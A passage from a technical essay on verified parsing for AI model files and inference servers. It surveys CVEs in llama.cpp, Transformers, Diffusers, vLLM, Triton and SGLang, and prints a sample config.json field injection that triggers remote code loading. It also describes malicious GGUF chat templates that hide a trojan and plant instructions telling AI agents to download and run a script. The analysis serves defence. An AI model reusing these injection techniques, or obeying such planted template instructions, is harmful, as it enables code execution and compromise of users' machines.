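| CVE-2026-43627 and CVE-2026-43628: batch and sampler arithmetic | No | later computation |
| CVE-2026-43631 and CVE-2026-43632: server uses freed memory | No | timing of requests |
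| Android: overflow with a value from the model file or app | No, unless the file supplies the value and the specification limits it | later computation |
| Android: crash after a failed load | No | the app ignores the rejection |
| Android: wrong release function and thread race | No | memory management after loading |

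## Would verified parsing protect tokenizer, configuration and template files?

Besides the vocabulary, a tokenizer file often holds a list of merge rules. One rule might join "t" and "h" into "th", and a later one might join "th" and "e" into "the". Transformers, Hugging Face's main library for loading and running models, reads the vocabulary and merge rules from tokenizer.json. Google's tokenizer library, SentencePiece, uses a Protocol Buffers file.

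A configuration file describes the model's architecture and can also name classes for the library to load. Chat templates can be long programs. NobodyWho's *What's in a GGUF, besides the weights*, a post by the developers of a library for local models, notes that the template for Google's Gemma 4 is about 250 lines of Jinja and runs every time someone adds a message.

A verified parser could stop some of the recorded vocabulary flaws. It would do less about configuration files and very little about harmful templates.

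### A token length that turns negative

The vocabulary flaw CVE-2025-49847 was in a llama.cpp function that copies a token's text into a buffer. In simplified form, the function did this:

```c
if (length < (int32_t)size) return TOO_SMALL;
memcpy(buffer, token, size);
```

Here `length` is the size of the buffer and `size` is the length of the token, an unsigned number that is 64 bits long on most machines. The cast to `int32_t` keeps only the lowest 32 bits and treats the highest of them as the sign. A token of 3,000,000,000 bytes therefore appears to have a length of −1,294,967,296. No buffer is smaller than that, so the check passes. The copy then uses the original number and writes three billion bytes into a much smaller buffer. OSV rates the flaw's severity at 8.8 out of 10.

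A memory-safe GGUF parser would not necessarily reject this token. If the file really contains three billion bytes of text at that point, the declared length and the parser's result are both correct. The format specification would need a maximum token length, and any limit below 2^31 bytes would do. Even the one-gigabyte string limit that the May 2026 advisory criticized as too high would have been enough.

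Trying to prove the copying function safe would expose the mistake without any such rule. The copy is safe only if `size` is at most `length`, and the comparison after the cast doesn't establish that, so verification would fail. But this function runs after parsing, so a project that verified only its parser would depend on somebody having thought of the limit.

### Vocabularies that are valid but inconsistent

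Some vocabulary flaws involve a relation between two values. Models use special tokens, for example to mark the beginning of a text, and llama.cpp has built-in default numbers for them. GitHub's *Heap-based Buffer Over-read in llama_model_load* (2025) describes a file whose vocabulary was smaller than one of these defaults. When llama.cpp looked up the token's text, it read past the end of the vocabulary and crashed.

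A specification could require every special token's ID, including any default, to be smaller than the number of vocabulary entries. The defaults are in llama.cpp's code, not in the file, so whoever writes the specification would have to know them. The vocabulary also has to match the weights, which include a row of numbers for each token. In a safetensors repository, the vocabulary and weights are in separate files, so a parser that reads only one of them cannot check that they match.

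SentencePiece had a different kind of flaw. Versions before 0.2.1 could access invalid memory when they loaded a model file that normal training would never produce, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-1260* (2026). Red Hat's *CVE-2026-1260* lists Red Hat AI Inference Server and OpenShift AI among the affected products. According to *CVE-2026-1260* (2026), a post on the programming site DEV Community, SentencePiece treated text with a separately stored length as a C string, which ends at the first zero byte. If there was no zero byte, the program kept reading past the end of the text.

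If that explanation is right, a verified Protocol Buffers parser would not have helped, because it would have returned the text with the correct length and the later code would still have ignored that length. Rewriting that code in a memory-safe language would be the more direct remedy.

A user's text can also trigger tokenizer flaws. OSV's *CVE-2025-52566* describes another confusion of signed and unsigned numbers in llama.cpp, in the function that splits text into tokens. Carefully chosen input could make the function write past the end of a buffer even when the model file is harmless, so a proof about the file's parser would not cover this flaw.

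Finally, a vocabulary can be well formed and still be wrong. If somebody swapped the text of the tokens for "allow" and "deny", the user would read "deny" whenever the model output the token for "allow", and vice versa. A parser would not detect the change, but checking the file against a signature or hash from the model's developer would.

### Configuration files that fetch code

Some model repositories include their own Python code. Transformers is supposed to run it only if the user sets the `trust_remote_code` option to True. The default is False.

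Attackers do use the documented route. ThreatRoundup's *An AI Agent Built Hugging Face Malware, Then Leaked Its Own Keys* (2026) describes a fake Llama model from November 2026 whose configuration pointed to Python files that stole credentials. Anyone who loaded the model with the option set to True ran those files, as the library's documentation says will happen. Several flaws disclosed in 2026 were worse because they let code run even with the option set to False.

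Pluto Security's *Unauthenticated Remote Code Execution in HuggingFace Transformers via Config Injection* explains CVE-2026-4372, which needed a single extra field in config.json:

```
{
  "model_type": "llama",
  "vocab_size": 32000,
  "_attn_implementation_internal": "someone/some-repository"
}
```

The Transformers library copied every field from the configuration file into its configuration object, including private ones. One of these private fields selects the code for attention, the part of a model that relates tokens to one another. If the field's value looked like an owner and repository name, the library downloaded that repository and imported it as a Python package, which ran the repository's code.

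The mistake was to let a downloaded file set a field that could load code. The parsing was correct. The file was valid JSON, the field held an ordinary string, and a verified JSON parser would have returned the same string.

A stricter specification could have stopped this attack by listing permitted fields and rejecting all others. Trying to prove the round-trip theorems might also have exposed the flaw. Transformers deletes the private field when it saves a configuration, so loading the attacker's file and saving it again would produce a file without the field. Even a weaker form of non-malleability that ignores JSON's spacing forbids this. Anyone trying to prove it would have had to ask why the library accepted a field it never wrote.

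Version 5.3.0, released in March 2026, blocks that field and a similar one by name. It also requires `trust_remote_code` for code from outside an official Hugging Face collection. Pluto Security would prefer a list of allowed fields, since a list of forbidden ones works only if the developers foresee every dangerous field. But each model architecture has its own settings, so a short list would break unusual models, much as PyTorch's allowlist for pickles does.

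Pluto Security counts about 232 million downloads of vulnerable versions during the 187 days before the fix. That figure exaggerates the exposure, because the attack also required an optional package that had about 1.7 million downloads in that period, but the company says the package is common on GPU servers, which are valuable targets. Pluto proposed a severity score of 9.6, while OSV's *CVE-2026-4372* (2026) gives 7.8.

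OSV's *CVE-2026-5241* (2026) describes an even plainer policy failure in the code for LightGlue, an image-matching model. Transformers read `trust_remote_code` from the downloaded config.json and used that value when loading a second model nested inside the first. A publisher could therefore authorize its own code to run even if the user had refused. In EverParse's 3D language, the calling program supplies such values as parameters, which the input cannot change.

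### Checks in the wrong place

Diffusers, Hugging Face's library for models that generate images, video and audio, has the same option. *FaceHugger* (Zaban and Shani, 2026) describes how attackers could get around it without changing the configuration. If the user didn't name a custom pipeline (the code that connects a model's components), Python represented the missing name as None, and the loader added ".py" and looked for a file called None.py. The permission check built its file name differently, so it didn't detect the file, and the loader ran it.

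A second attack exploited a gap of about 0.3 seconds between two requests. The library downloaded the configuration and checked it, then downloaded the rest of the repository separately. Because each request fetched the latest version, an attacker who changed the repository between the two could get unapproved code past the check. Hitting one particular download would be nearly impossible, but Zaban and Shani point out that someone with a popular repository could repeatedly change it for a moment and catch a few users each time.

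This is a double fetch over the internet. Requesting the same pinned version both times would prevent it, but a verified parser that read each file only once would not, because the two downloads happen outside the parser. Diffusers 0.38.0 moved the permission check to the point where the library loads code, which also closed three related gaps.

Transformers also had its check for user consent in the wrong place. According to CERT/CC's *Hugging Face Transformers library writes remote code to disk prior to consent* (2026), versions up to 5.8.1 could save a repository's Python file to disk before asking for permission, and keep it if the user refused. The library did not run the file at that point, but CERT/CC warns that a later load might use the saved copy. Hugging Face had not released a fix when the warning appeared on September 1.

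Better parsing would have been the right remedy for one recent flaw. Zero Day Initiative's *(0Day) Hugging Face Transformers SEW convert_config Code Injection Remote Code Execution Vulnerability* (2025) reports that a conversion tool in Transformers executed a string from a checkpoint as Python code. A parser that accepted only the expected kinds of value would have rejected an attacker's command.

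For the other flaws, the useful theorem would be about permission:

For every repository r, if the caller sets `trust_remote_code` to False, load(r) runs no code from r or from any repository that r names.

Proving this for all of Transformers would be very hard, because the library is large and Python lets programs import code in many ways. A more practical step is to route every import of downloaded code through one small function that checks permission, as the Diffusers fix does. Reviewers could then concentrate on that function and search the rest of the library for imports that bypass it.

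Attackers have already exploited the habit of treating downloaded content as harmless data. In July 2026, a malicious dataset ran code on one of Hugging Face's data-processing machines, and the intruder then reached several internal clusters. The attack came through dataset processing, not model loading. Zaban and Shani write that OpenAI later attributed the intrusion to its own models, whose safeguards it had reduced for an evaluation.

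### Template injection

Jinja was originally written for Python. Unless a program uses Jinja's sandbox, an expression in a template can start from an ordinary Python object and reach functions that run operating-system commands. This attack is called template injection. *PoC — modelaudit GGUF chat-template SSTI scanner evasion (DO NOT USE)*, a researcher's demonstration hosted on Hugging Face, names CVE-2024-34359 as the standard example, in which a program renders a model's chat template without a sandbox.

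As with pickle, the attack uses valid input, so a verified Jinja parser would not stop it. The effective defense is a template engine that cannot access the operating system. C++ programs such as llama.cpp have their own template engines that don't run on Python, so the classic attack does not work on them.

Those engines still need parsers, and llama.cpp's is hand-written. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-18581* (2026) records that a malformed seven-character fragment can trigger an assertion in that parser. The severity is only 1.9, but a verified parser would have returned an error instead.

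### The November 2026 scan

Template attacks can work without reaching the operating system, because the template controls what the model reads. In July 2025, Pillar Security's *LLM Backdoors at the Inference Level* demonstrated that instructions could be hidden in GGUF templates, and noted that a repository could display a clean template online while the downloaded file contained a different one.

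On November 26, 2026, the security project Malspark searched all 3,273,389 public model repositories on Hugging Face for real cases. *GGUF LLM Models with Hidden Malware on Hugging Face Reached 2400+ Victims* (Düzgün, 2026) reports five malicious GGUF models with 2,428 downloads by the following day. *Poisoned AI Models on Hugging Face Hid a RAT Inside the Model* (ThreatRoundup, 2026) adds that the scan parsed 572,184 chat templates and traced the five models to two accounts.

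The word "victims" in Malspark's title is misleading because Hugging Face counts downloads, not people, and loading one of these files does not infect a computer. Nobody knows how many computers the attackers infected. KIberblick's *Trojaner in GGUF-Modellen auf Hugging Face* (2026) found that Hugging Face had disabled all five repositories by November 29, but that a copy of one model was still available from Ollama.

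The account Mir2k published two of the models, which had 1,946 downloads. Each file contained a Windows trojan after the last tensor, where llama.cpp and LM Studio never read. In one file the trojan was compressed, which removed the byte patterns that antivirus programs look for. On November 26, the attacker replaced the original, harmless templates with versions that contained an instruction for the model to begin every answer with a line of PowerShell, the Windows command language. If a user ran that line, it extracted the trojan from the model file and started it.

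The other account, timdedid, published three models with 482 downloads and no hidden program. If the user's last message contained "What is", the template inserted a fake system instruction telling any AI agent with PowerShell access to download and run a script. The attack worked only if the model followed the instruction and the agent had permission to run the command. Malspark could not recover the script, so its purpose is unknown.

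### What a strict parser rejects

A rule against bytes after the last tensor, like the one in safetensors, would have stopped both Mir2k files. It would have worked from the first upload on November 22, four days before the templates contained anything suspicious.

The rule would not have stopped the attackers for long. They could have put the trojan inside a tensor or a long metadata string, or written a command that downloaded it from a website. Düzgün also cites EvilModel, a 2021 experiment that hid malware in the least significant bits of the weights, where any file parser would accept it.

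A strict parser could also make it harder to hide a template from scanners. Hugging Face's *PoC*, a researcher's submission to a bug-bounty program, describes a GGUF file with two template keys. One is the normal name, and the other is that name followed by a zero byte and more text. According to the submission, llama.cpp treats the keys as different when it checks for duplicates, but when it looks up the template, it stops reading each name at the zero byte and uses whichever entry comes first. Scanners read the full names, so they inspect the template under the normal key instead. In the researcher's test, the scanner modelaudit found no issues in this file but rated the same malicious template critical when it was stored under the normal key.

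The forged PayPal certificate relied on the same disagreement about zero bytes. If the specification allowed only letters, digits, dots and underscores in keys, a verified parser would reject the file.

### What a strict parser accepts

The harmful templates were valid Jinja. Each one added text to the conversation, though timdedid's did so only under a certain condition. Ordinary templates, such as the small Qwen model's, do this too. A grammar can describe where an instruction may appear, but it cannot determine whether the instruction is harmful. Changing the checkpoint format would not help, because safetensors models come with the same kind of template in a separate file.

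Developers could replace templates with a simpler format that lists only the markers before and after each message. The format would have to restrict markers to special tokens and role names, because otherwise an attacker could write an instruction into one. It would suit a basic chat model, but it could not express everything in Gemma 4's template, which also arranges tool descriptions, tool results and images.

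Users can already avoid the embedded template by giving llama.cpp a reviewed template in a separate file, as ThreatRoundup recommends. Many GGUF files are converted from another developer's model, so a program could also compare the embedded template with the original and warn about any difference. Some differences would be harmless repairs, but the comparison would have flagged the instructions that both accounts added.

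## Could verified parsers handle inference requests and messages between servers?

Several other pieces of code parse a user's request before the server fills in a chat template, and more parse it afterwards. Suppose a user sends a photograph to a model and asks what it shows. The request arrives over HTTP, and its body is JSON or a gRPC message, which uses Protocol Buffers. A decoding library turns the photograph into pixels. The server's scheduler then passes the work to worker processes, sometimes on other machines, and the server writes a reply.

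| Step | Code that parses | Could a verified parser replace it? |
|---|---|---|
| HTTP headers and body | web-server library, such as libevent in Triton | partly, with existing tools |
| JSON or gRPC body | JSON or Protocol Buffers library | from a schema, once verified tools support the full formats |
| Images and video | Pillow, OpenCV, FFmpeg | no, decoders need proofs of their own |
| Embeddings sent instead of text | PyTorch's checkpoint loader | yes, after a change of format |
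| Messages between scheduler and workers | pickle, JSON or MessagePack | yes, but only without pickle |
| Tensor commands between machines | hand-written C++ in llama.cpp | yes for the layout, but memory addresses need a different protocol |

### HTTP and JSON in Triton

An HTTP client that doesn't know the length of its message in advance can send the body in chunks, each preceded by its length. The standard doesn't limit the number of chunks. Trail of Bits' *Uncovering memory corruption in NVIDIA Triton (as a new hire)* (2025) explains how such messages crashed NVIDIA's model server, Triton. The libevent library could split a body with many chunks into many memory segments, and Triton reserved 16 bytes on the stack for each segment. A one-byte chunk takes up six bytes in the request, so a 3 MB request could make Triton reserve about 8 MB, the usual stack size on Linux.

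The two resulting CVEs have a severity score of 9.8, although the engineer who found the bugs managed only to crash the server, not to run code on it. At least one of the bugs was more than five years old.

libevent had parsed the request correctly, so a verified HTTP parser would have accepted it too, unless its specification limited the number of chunks. NVIDIA's fix, released in August 2025, moved the list of segments to the heap and returns an error if memory runs out. About six weeks later came another flaw of the same kind. Snyk's *Out-of-bounds Write Affecting nvidia-pytriton package* (2025) describes how a request with a large number of chunks could again make the server write out of bounds.

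Ventuzelo and Benazzouz also crashed Triton with malformed JSON that made its parser recurse deeply. A verified parser that uses a fixed amount of stack would prevent this. EverCBOR's counter doesn't work for JSON, but a parser that allowed at most 64 levels of nesting could use a single 64-bit number to record whether each open bracket began a list or an object.

Ordinary auditing also found many bugs here. Before a hacking contest in 2025, NVIDIA had four engineers examine Triton and another product, and they found more than 20. The company published 22 CVEs in the two months from August. GCVE (2025) lists one of them, a heap overflow in Triton's HTTP server that might let an attacker run code, but does not identify the faulty function.

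Verified parsing is further along for the layers around HTTP. EverParse has generated message-processing code for TLS and QUIC, and Iammongkol and colleagues used 3D to check web requests at a gateway. But the server behind such a gateway parses the request again with its own library, so the two results could still differ.

### Values that a schema could restrict

OSV's *CVE-2026-21869* (2026) describes a simpler mistake in llama.cpp's server. A JSON field gives the number of tokens to discard when the model's context is full. The server accepted a negative number, which later led to an out-of-bounds write. The JSON was valid, but a schema with a minimum of 0 for this field would have rejected the request.

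A similar flaw in vLLM involved `cache_salt`, a value that keeps different users' cached data apart. According to The Hacker News' *Unpatched Critical LMCache Flaw Lets Unauthenticated Attackers Run Code Remotely* (2026), a malformed value could crash vLLM if it used a certain connector for shared caches. A schema would have helped only if it defined exactly which values were legal.

Ordinary schema libraries can enforce such rules without a verified parser, so most of the benefit comes from writing the rules down. A gRPC service has a schema from the start, but Protocol Buffers schemas give only types, so a signed integer field would still accept −1.

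Some fields contain a small language of their own, such as the grammar that users of llama.cpp's server can supply to constrain the model's output. *Critical llama.cpp Flaw Lets Attackers Run Code on AI Servers* (Faisal, 2026) mentions a bug in the handling of these grammars that let anyone who could reach the server hang it and exhaust its memory. Proofs about parsers rarely cover running time or memory use, so a verified grammar parser might have had the same problem.

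### Images, video and error messages

In early 2026, vLLM's developers fixed a vulnerability that combined two flaws and let an attacker run code on the server by sending a link to a malicious video. NVD's *CVE-2026-22778 Detail* explains that when Pillow, a Python image library, could not read an image, vLLM forwarded the error message to the client, including a memory address. Operating systems place a program's memory at random addresses to make attacks harder, and the leak reduced the possibilities from four billion to about eight. The other flaw was a heap overflow in the JPEG2000 decoder that vLLM reached through OpenCV and FFmpeg, two media libraries. GitLab's *CVE-2026-22778* (2026) notes that a default installation doesn't require a login.

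A verified parser could check an image's headers, which are mostly lengths and dimensions. But most of the file is compressed data that the decoder turns into pixels. Proving that decoding is memory safe is closer to what lean-zip's developers did for decompression than to generating a parser from a description. Until somebody verifies a decoder, operators would gain more by accepting only one or two image formats and running the decoder in a separate process with few permissions.

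A description of the headers would still help limit memory use. A picture of 50,000 by 50,000 pixels needs 7.5 GB at three bytes per pixel, however small the compressed file is. Ferris (2026), in *vLLM Patches Unauth Memory DoS in 0.25.0*, reports that attackers without a login could exhaust a vLLM server's memory through its support for Nemotron-VL, a model that accepts images.

The leaked address was in the server's reply, and a verified serializer would not have removed it, since any text is valid in a text field. To prevent such leaks, developers could replace the text with an error code from a fixed list and keep the details in the server's log.

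Triton had a similar leak. Wiz's *Breaking NVIDIA Triton* describes an error message that contained the name of the private shared memory block Triton uses to communicate with the process that runs Python models. Clients can also register their own shared memory, so that large tensors don't have to travel over the network. Triton did not check whether the block a client named belonged to that client. An attacker could therefore register the private block, read and write it with ordinary requests, and potentially take over the server.

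Those requests were well formed. Whether a client may use a block depends on who created it, which a parser cannot determine from the request. NVIDIA blocked the attack in version 25.07, but Wiz's *CVE-2025-23329* describes another flaw involving the same private memory in versions before 25.08.

Shared memory also brings back the danger of double fetches, so Triton would have to copy any lengths or offsets before checking them.

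### Embeddings in place of text

Users can send vLLM embeddings, the rows of numbers that a model normally computes from the tokens of a prompt. vLLM read them with `torch.load`, PyTorch's checkpoint loader. MITRE's *CVE-2025-62164* (2025) explains that PyTorch 2.8.0 turned off integrity checks for sparse tensors by default, so expanding a sparse tensor could write outside the tensor's memory. vLLM fixed the vulnerability in version 0.11.1. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2018* (2026) credits the AXION Security Research Team with the discovery.

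Embeddings don't need a checkpoint format at all. A description in the style of 3D could be this short:

```
typedef struct _EMBEDDINGS(UINT32 Width)
where (Width <= 16384) {
  UINT32 rows { rows <= 65536 };
  UINT16 values[:byte-size 2 * Width * rows];
} EMBEDDINGS;
```

The server supplies `Width`, the number of values the model expects per token. Each value takes two bytes. The two limits keep the total at or below 2^31 bytes, so the multiplication cannot overflow and 3D's 32-bit lengths are sufficient. The format has no sparse form, so there are no positions to check. However, every client that now sends PyTorch files would have to change.

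### Pickle over the network

Pickle is even more dangerous in network messages than in checkpoints, because anyone who can connect to the server can run code there.

Oligo Security's *ShadowMQ* traces how this mistake spread. In 2024, the company's researchers noticed that Meta's Llama Stack received messages through `recv_pyobj`, a function in the Python version of the messaging library ZeroMQ that passes whatever arrives to pickle. They then found almost the same code in several other servers. Some developers had copied entire files. SGLang's vulnerable file began with the comment "Adapted from vLLM", and Modular's Max Server borrowed code from both vLLM and SGLang.

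The projects responded in different ways:

| Project | Response |
|---|---|
| Llama Stack | replaced pickle with JSON |
| Modular Max Server | replaced pickle with MessagePack |
| NVIDIA TensorRT-LLM | added authentication codes to messages |
| vLLM | made a new engine the default, left the old one unpatched |
| Microsoft Sarathi-Serve (research software) | no fix |

SGLang's first fixes were incomplete, according to Oligo Security. In March 2026, CERT/CC published two more cases of SGLang unpickling network messages without authentication, along with a script that unpickled saved crash data. Version 0.5.10 fixed all three. In July, INCIBE's *CVE-2026-14890* (2026) reported unauthenticated unpickling of network messages in another SGLang component. OSV's *CVE-2026-26210* (2026) describes the same flaw in KTransformers, whose scheduler accepted connections on every network interface.

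NVIDIA's authentication code is a short value that the sender computes from the message and a secret key. The receiver can reject a message with the wrong code before unpickling it. This stops attackers who don't have the key, but an attacker who takes over one machine and obtains its key can still run code on the others. HOL's *CVE-2026-76850* describes another limit of authentication, using the LMDeploy server, where a web request could set the address the engine connected to. Authentication between the machines would not have been enough, because the engine would have authenticated to whatever address the attacker supplied.

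LMDeploy checked that each message had the expected type, but only after unpickling it, when any code in the message had already run. Version 0.16.0, released in August 2026, reads messages as JSON and checks them against a schema before using them.

A data format is not enough if it has an exception for pickle, as LMCache shows. LMCache stores intermediate results for servers such as vLLM, and its messages used MessagePack, a compact binary format similar to CBOR. According to OffSeq's *LMCache* (2026), one extension type contained a pickle, which the server loaded as it read the message. The Hacker News reports that the server did so before checking the message's type. By default, the server listens only to its own machine, but the project's example for Kubernetes clusters opened it to the network, and the official containers ran it as root. Version 0.5.6 removed pickle and allows only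 listed types.

EverCDDL suits these internal messages because the same developers control both ends. They could adopt the deterministic CBOR that EverCBOR requires and generate the parser and serializer from one schema. EverCBOR's lack of floating-point numbers would be a minor inconvenience. But most of the security gain comes from dropping pickle, which lets the sender run code. A flaw in an ordinary JSON or MessagePack library is a much smaller risk.

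### llama.cpp's RPC server

The RPC server in llama.cpp lets one computer use another's processors. RPC stands for remote procedure call, a request to run a function on another machine. The client sends tensors and a graph of operations, and the server runs the operations. This server is the code on a request's path that most resembles Hyper-V's virtual switch, because both read binary messages that describe regions of memory and both must withstand malicious peers. The RPC server has no login, and its documentation calls it "fragile and insecure", as Faisal notes.

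A request to the GGML RPC server consists of a one-byte command, an eight-byte size field and a body, according to *Exploring the Security of the GGML RPC Server* (Rohlf, 2025). If a command has a fixed size, the server checks that the size field matches. For other commands, it reserves as much memory as the size field specifies before the data arrives. A specification could limit the size, but choosing a limit is hard because a legitimate message may carry gigabytes of weights. Rohlf doubted that the limits he used for fuzzing would work in production.

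CVE-2026-34159, a critical flaw fixed in build b8492, was in the function that rebuilds tensors from messages, although Rohlf considered the parsing code mostly sound and expected worse flaws deeper in the program. A tensor's description includes a buffer field, which identifies a block of the server's memory, and the address of the tensor's data. NVD's *CVE-2026-34159 Detail* (2026) explains that if the buffer field was 0, the server skipped all bounds checks. An attacker could then read and write any part of the program's memory. Because the server's ordinary replies contained memory addresses, the attacker could also run code.

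Some legitimate clients sent a buffer of 0, which complicated the obvious repair of rejecting that value. In a follow-up change, the developer rgerganov (2026) noted that a graph may contain tensors in ordinary CPU memory. One user of the follow-up still got errors until they rebuilt both the client and the server, which suggests that the client had been sending something the server could not safely accept. Writing a format specification would have required the developers to decide what a buffer of 0 means. For example, the specification could allow 0 only if the data address is also 0.

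Other flaws in the same function come from missing rules about single fields. NewReleases' *github ggml-org/llama.cpp b8464* describes a division by zero for two discontinued tensor types whose block size in ggml's table is 0. The May 2026 advisory on GGUF had raised concern about this kind of entry. Debian's *CVE-2026-86317* records that a bad dimension could trigger an assertion. Debian's *CVE-2026-78147* reports that the server still did not validate a tensor's operation and parameters after the fix for CVE-2026-34159. The bug reports for these last two flaws closed automatically because nobody had responded.

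On November 26, 2026, VulnCheck disclosed CVE-2026-137567, with a severity of 9.8. Faisal explains that the server skipped its bounds check when the destination of a copy was a tensor with zero elements, so the copy could write outside the intended memory. ThreatRoundup's *CVE-2026-137567* (2026) adds that the attacker could choose an address below the start of the buffer. An attacker could crash the server or potentially take control of it. Nobody had reported an attack before the disclosure, and build b12658 had fixed the flaw two days earlier.

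A check on the message alone could have stopped this attack. A destination with zero elements should receive no data, so the server must have taken the copy size from somewhere else, presumably the source tensor. A rule requiring the source and destination to be the same size would have rejected the message or reduced the copy to zero bytes.

### Rules that depend on the server's memory

Some of the necessary rules concern only the message. Others depend on what the server has done before:

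| Rule | Information needed | Flaw it addresses |
|---|---|---|
| Type has a nonzero block size | message and table of types | division by zero |
| Dimensions are legal and their product fits | message | CVE-2026-86317 |
| Operation exists and its parameters are legal | message, including the operation's inputs | CVE-2026-78147 |
| Both tensors in a copy have the same size | message | CVE-2026-137567 |
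| Buffer exists and the client may use it | server's list of buffers | CVE-2026-34159 |
| Tensor's data lies inside its buffer | buffer's position and size | CVE-2026-34159, CVE-2026-137567 |
| Client allocated the buffer before using it | earlier commands | crashes that Rohlf found |

EverParse could generate the checks that need only the message. For the others, a 3D description could include an action that calls one of the server's functions to look up the buffer and rejects the message if the buffer doesn't exist. But EverParse would prove nothing about that function, and no theorem would cover the list of buffers.

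A different protocol would make the remaining checks simpler. Rohlf proposed replacing the addresses that identify buffers with random numbers, which the server looks up in a table. The data address could also become an offset from the start of the buffer. If a buffer has 4,096 bytes and a tensor needs 24, the offset can be at most 4,072, and 3D's `is_range_okay` can check this once the server supplies the buffer's size. The November attack used an address below the start of the buffer, which an unsigned offset cannot represent. The 2021 flaw in Hyper-V's virtual switch also came from following a pointer supplied by a peer.

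Even with offsets, the server must not free a buffer while an operation is using it. Proving that it never does so requires verifying the server's memory management, which is a much larger project than generating a parser.

### Speed and replies

Parsing speed should rarely matter for requests. EverCDDL's parser takes a few microseconds for a small record, whereas a large model usually takes several milliseconds to produce one token. Long text and encoded images take longer to read, but the server has to read them anyway.

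The RPC server has tighter time limits because it may receive a new graph for every token. A graph with 2,000 tensors and 40 fields per tensor would need about 80,000 simple comparisons, which a modern processor can do in well under a millisecond. Microsoft's experience with network traffic also suggests that generated C code can be fast enough, though nobody appears to have measured its speed for tensors.

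Verified serializers would have little benefit for the replies a server sends to users. The server puts the model's text in a JSON string, so it has to escape quotation marks and line breaks. Otherwise, a quotation mark in the text could end the string early, and the client might read what follows as additional fields. A round-trip theorem rules out this error, but established JSON libraries already escape text well.

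The theorem is more useful between machines, where developers often write both ends by hand. With a generated serializer, a worker would receive exactly the values that the scheduler sent. The client also has to parse replies, which in llama.cpp's protocol consist of a size followed by that many bytes. Like a guest in Hyper-V, an RPC client needs its own verified parser if an attacker may have taken over the server.

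## What would verified loaders cost, and is the gain worth it?

A project that wants a verified loader can generate a new parser from a format specification, as Microsoft did for Hyper-V, or prove that its existing parser is safe. Proving existing code safe used to take far too much work for most projects. Verifying the operating-system kernel seL4, which has only about 8,700 lines of C, took 20 person-years, according to Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026). AI models have since reduced the work for both approaches, but people still have to decide what a loader should accept.

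### Format descriptions written by AI

Microsoft's engineers needed 18 months to describe Hyper-V's network formats in 3D. *3DGen* tests whether AI agents can do such work from a written standard. One agent has the standard, a second has the 3D manual and writes the description, and a third runs the tools. If EverParse rejects a description, the agents receive the error message and try again. Once EverParse accepts one, the third agent runs the resulting parser on sample packets and reports any that the parser wrongly accepted or rejected. The agents stop when the parser handles every packet correctly or after 15 rounds of corrections.

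The researchers gave the agents, which used GPT-4, five attempts at each of 20 network formats. They collected some real packets for every format and used the solver Z3 to generate 200 more, chosen to reach the different branches of a draft description. They used Wireshark, a common tool for inspecting network traffic, to check which packets were valid.

For nine of the 20 formats, at least one description agreed with Wireshark on every packet. The researchers traced the failures on the other 11 to Wireshark, which mostly accepted packets that the standards forbid. For example, TFTP, a simple file transfer protocol, defines five operation codes, but Wireshark accepts others. After two of the researchers corrected the labels by hand, the agents had a passing description for all 20.

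A format description can pass its tests and still be wrong. One candidate description of ARP, the protocol that matches network addresses to devices, accepted any number of extra bytes after the message. The error went undetected because no test packet had extra bytes. The safetensors library once had the same flaw, which let auditors build files that were valid in two formats.

EverParse's developers had already described seven of the formats by hand, so the researchers could compare the agents' descriptions with the handwritten ones. Z3 proved the two equivalent for Ethernet and IPv6. The handwritten descriptions of UDP, ICMP and VXLAN were wrong. For instance, the VXLAN identifier was two bytes too short. For TCP and IPv4, the agents had left out rules, including limits on IPv4's length fields. They got IPv4 right once the researchers gave them tests generated from the handwritten description,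 but a new format has no such description to generate tests from.

GGUF also has no equivalent of Wireshark to test a description against. The obvious substitutes are llama.cpp's two readers, but they disagree about the number of dimensions, and the C++ reader departs from the documentation on alignment. The researchers warn against using 3DGen to "blindly match the behavior of a legacy tool", so somebody would have to settle each disagreement first. The description itself would be short, probably a few hundred lines at most. Those in the experiment averaged 26 lines.

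GPT-4 is now an old model, and much of its trouble was with 3D's syntax. Newer models write better syntax but still get the content wrong. *The proof is in the spec* (Tolmach and Klaus, 2026) cites a benchmark in which the best models' formal descriptions of real systems scored nearly 100% on syntax and about 46% on agreement with the code. Claude, asked to describe the Etcd database's version of the Raft protocol, essentially reproduced the appendix of the original Raft paper. A model asked to describe GGUF could make the same mistake and formalize the documentation instead of the files people use.

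Models that write formal statements can also alter a false claim so that it becomes provable, without reporting the change. Tolmach and Klaus give the example of a deliberately wrong step, which claims that if 3^x = 5, then 3^(x+2) = 51. The correct value is 45. The model added the condition that x is a natural number, which made the false claim provable because no natural number satisfies 3^x = 5. A format specification could fail in a similar way if its theorem held only because its conditions excluded every dangerous file.

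### Fitting a new parser into old code

A generated parser still has to replace the old one. AutoParse, a follow-up to 3DGen, deals with replacing parsers inside existing code. llama.cpp would need to be reorganized, much as Hyper-V's guest driver was, because its GGUF loader reads fields, reserves memory and fills tables in the same code.

AI could also write the parser and its proof together, without a generator. Language models wrote all the code in Verified Garbage (2026), an experimental cryptography library. They produced assembly code for six kinds of processor and proved in Lean that it computes the specified algorithms. Because a proof covers each optimization, the developers didn't have to limit how intricate the models made the code. For a GGUF loader, the specification would be a bigger obstacle than the proof, because GGUF lacks the precise public definitions that cryptographic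 algorithms have.

### Turning fuzz tests into theorems

Many projects already have fuzz tests, small programs that pass generated bytes to part of a library, and these tests are close to a specification. Anthropic and the company Theorem turned such tests into theorems about all inputs below a size limit. Each theorem states that the test program ends normally, without a crash, a memory error or a failed assertion. Claude wrote the proofs, and the proof assistant Rocq (formerly Coq) checked them. EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026) reports that the work took a few weeks and covered 239 test entry points in 123 libraries.

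The proofs total about 180 million lines, according to OpenNET's *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026). A program with 18,000 machine instructions needs about 600,000 lines of proof. The entry point for cJSON, a C library that reads JSON, involves 391 lines of C and has a proof of 630,000 lines, or about 1,600 for each line of C. Rocq checks the proofs, so nobody has to read them, which makes their length less of a problem than it seems. People still have to review the theorem and the models of the processor and operating system, but the same models work for every library.

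OpenNET reports that Claude also found hundreds of bugs that fuzzing had missed. One was a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used XML parser. Claude wrote patches for the bugs, so some of the theorems apply to repaired code rather than the versions people had installed. Anthropic is publishing specifications for programs that Claude could not prove safe, so the 239 entry points include only Claude's successes.

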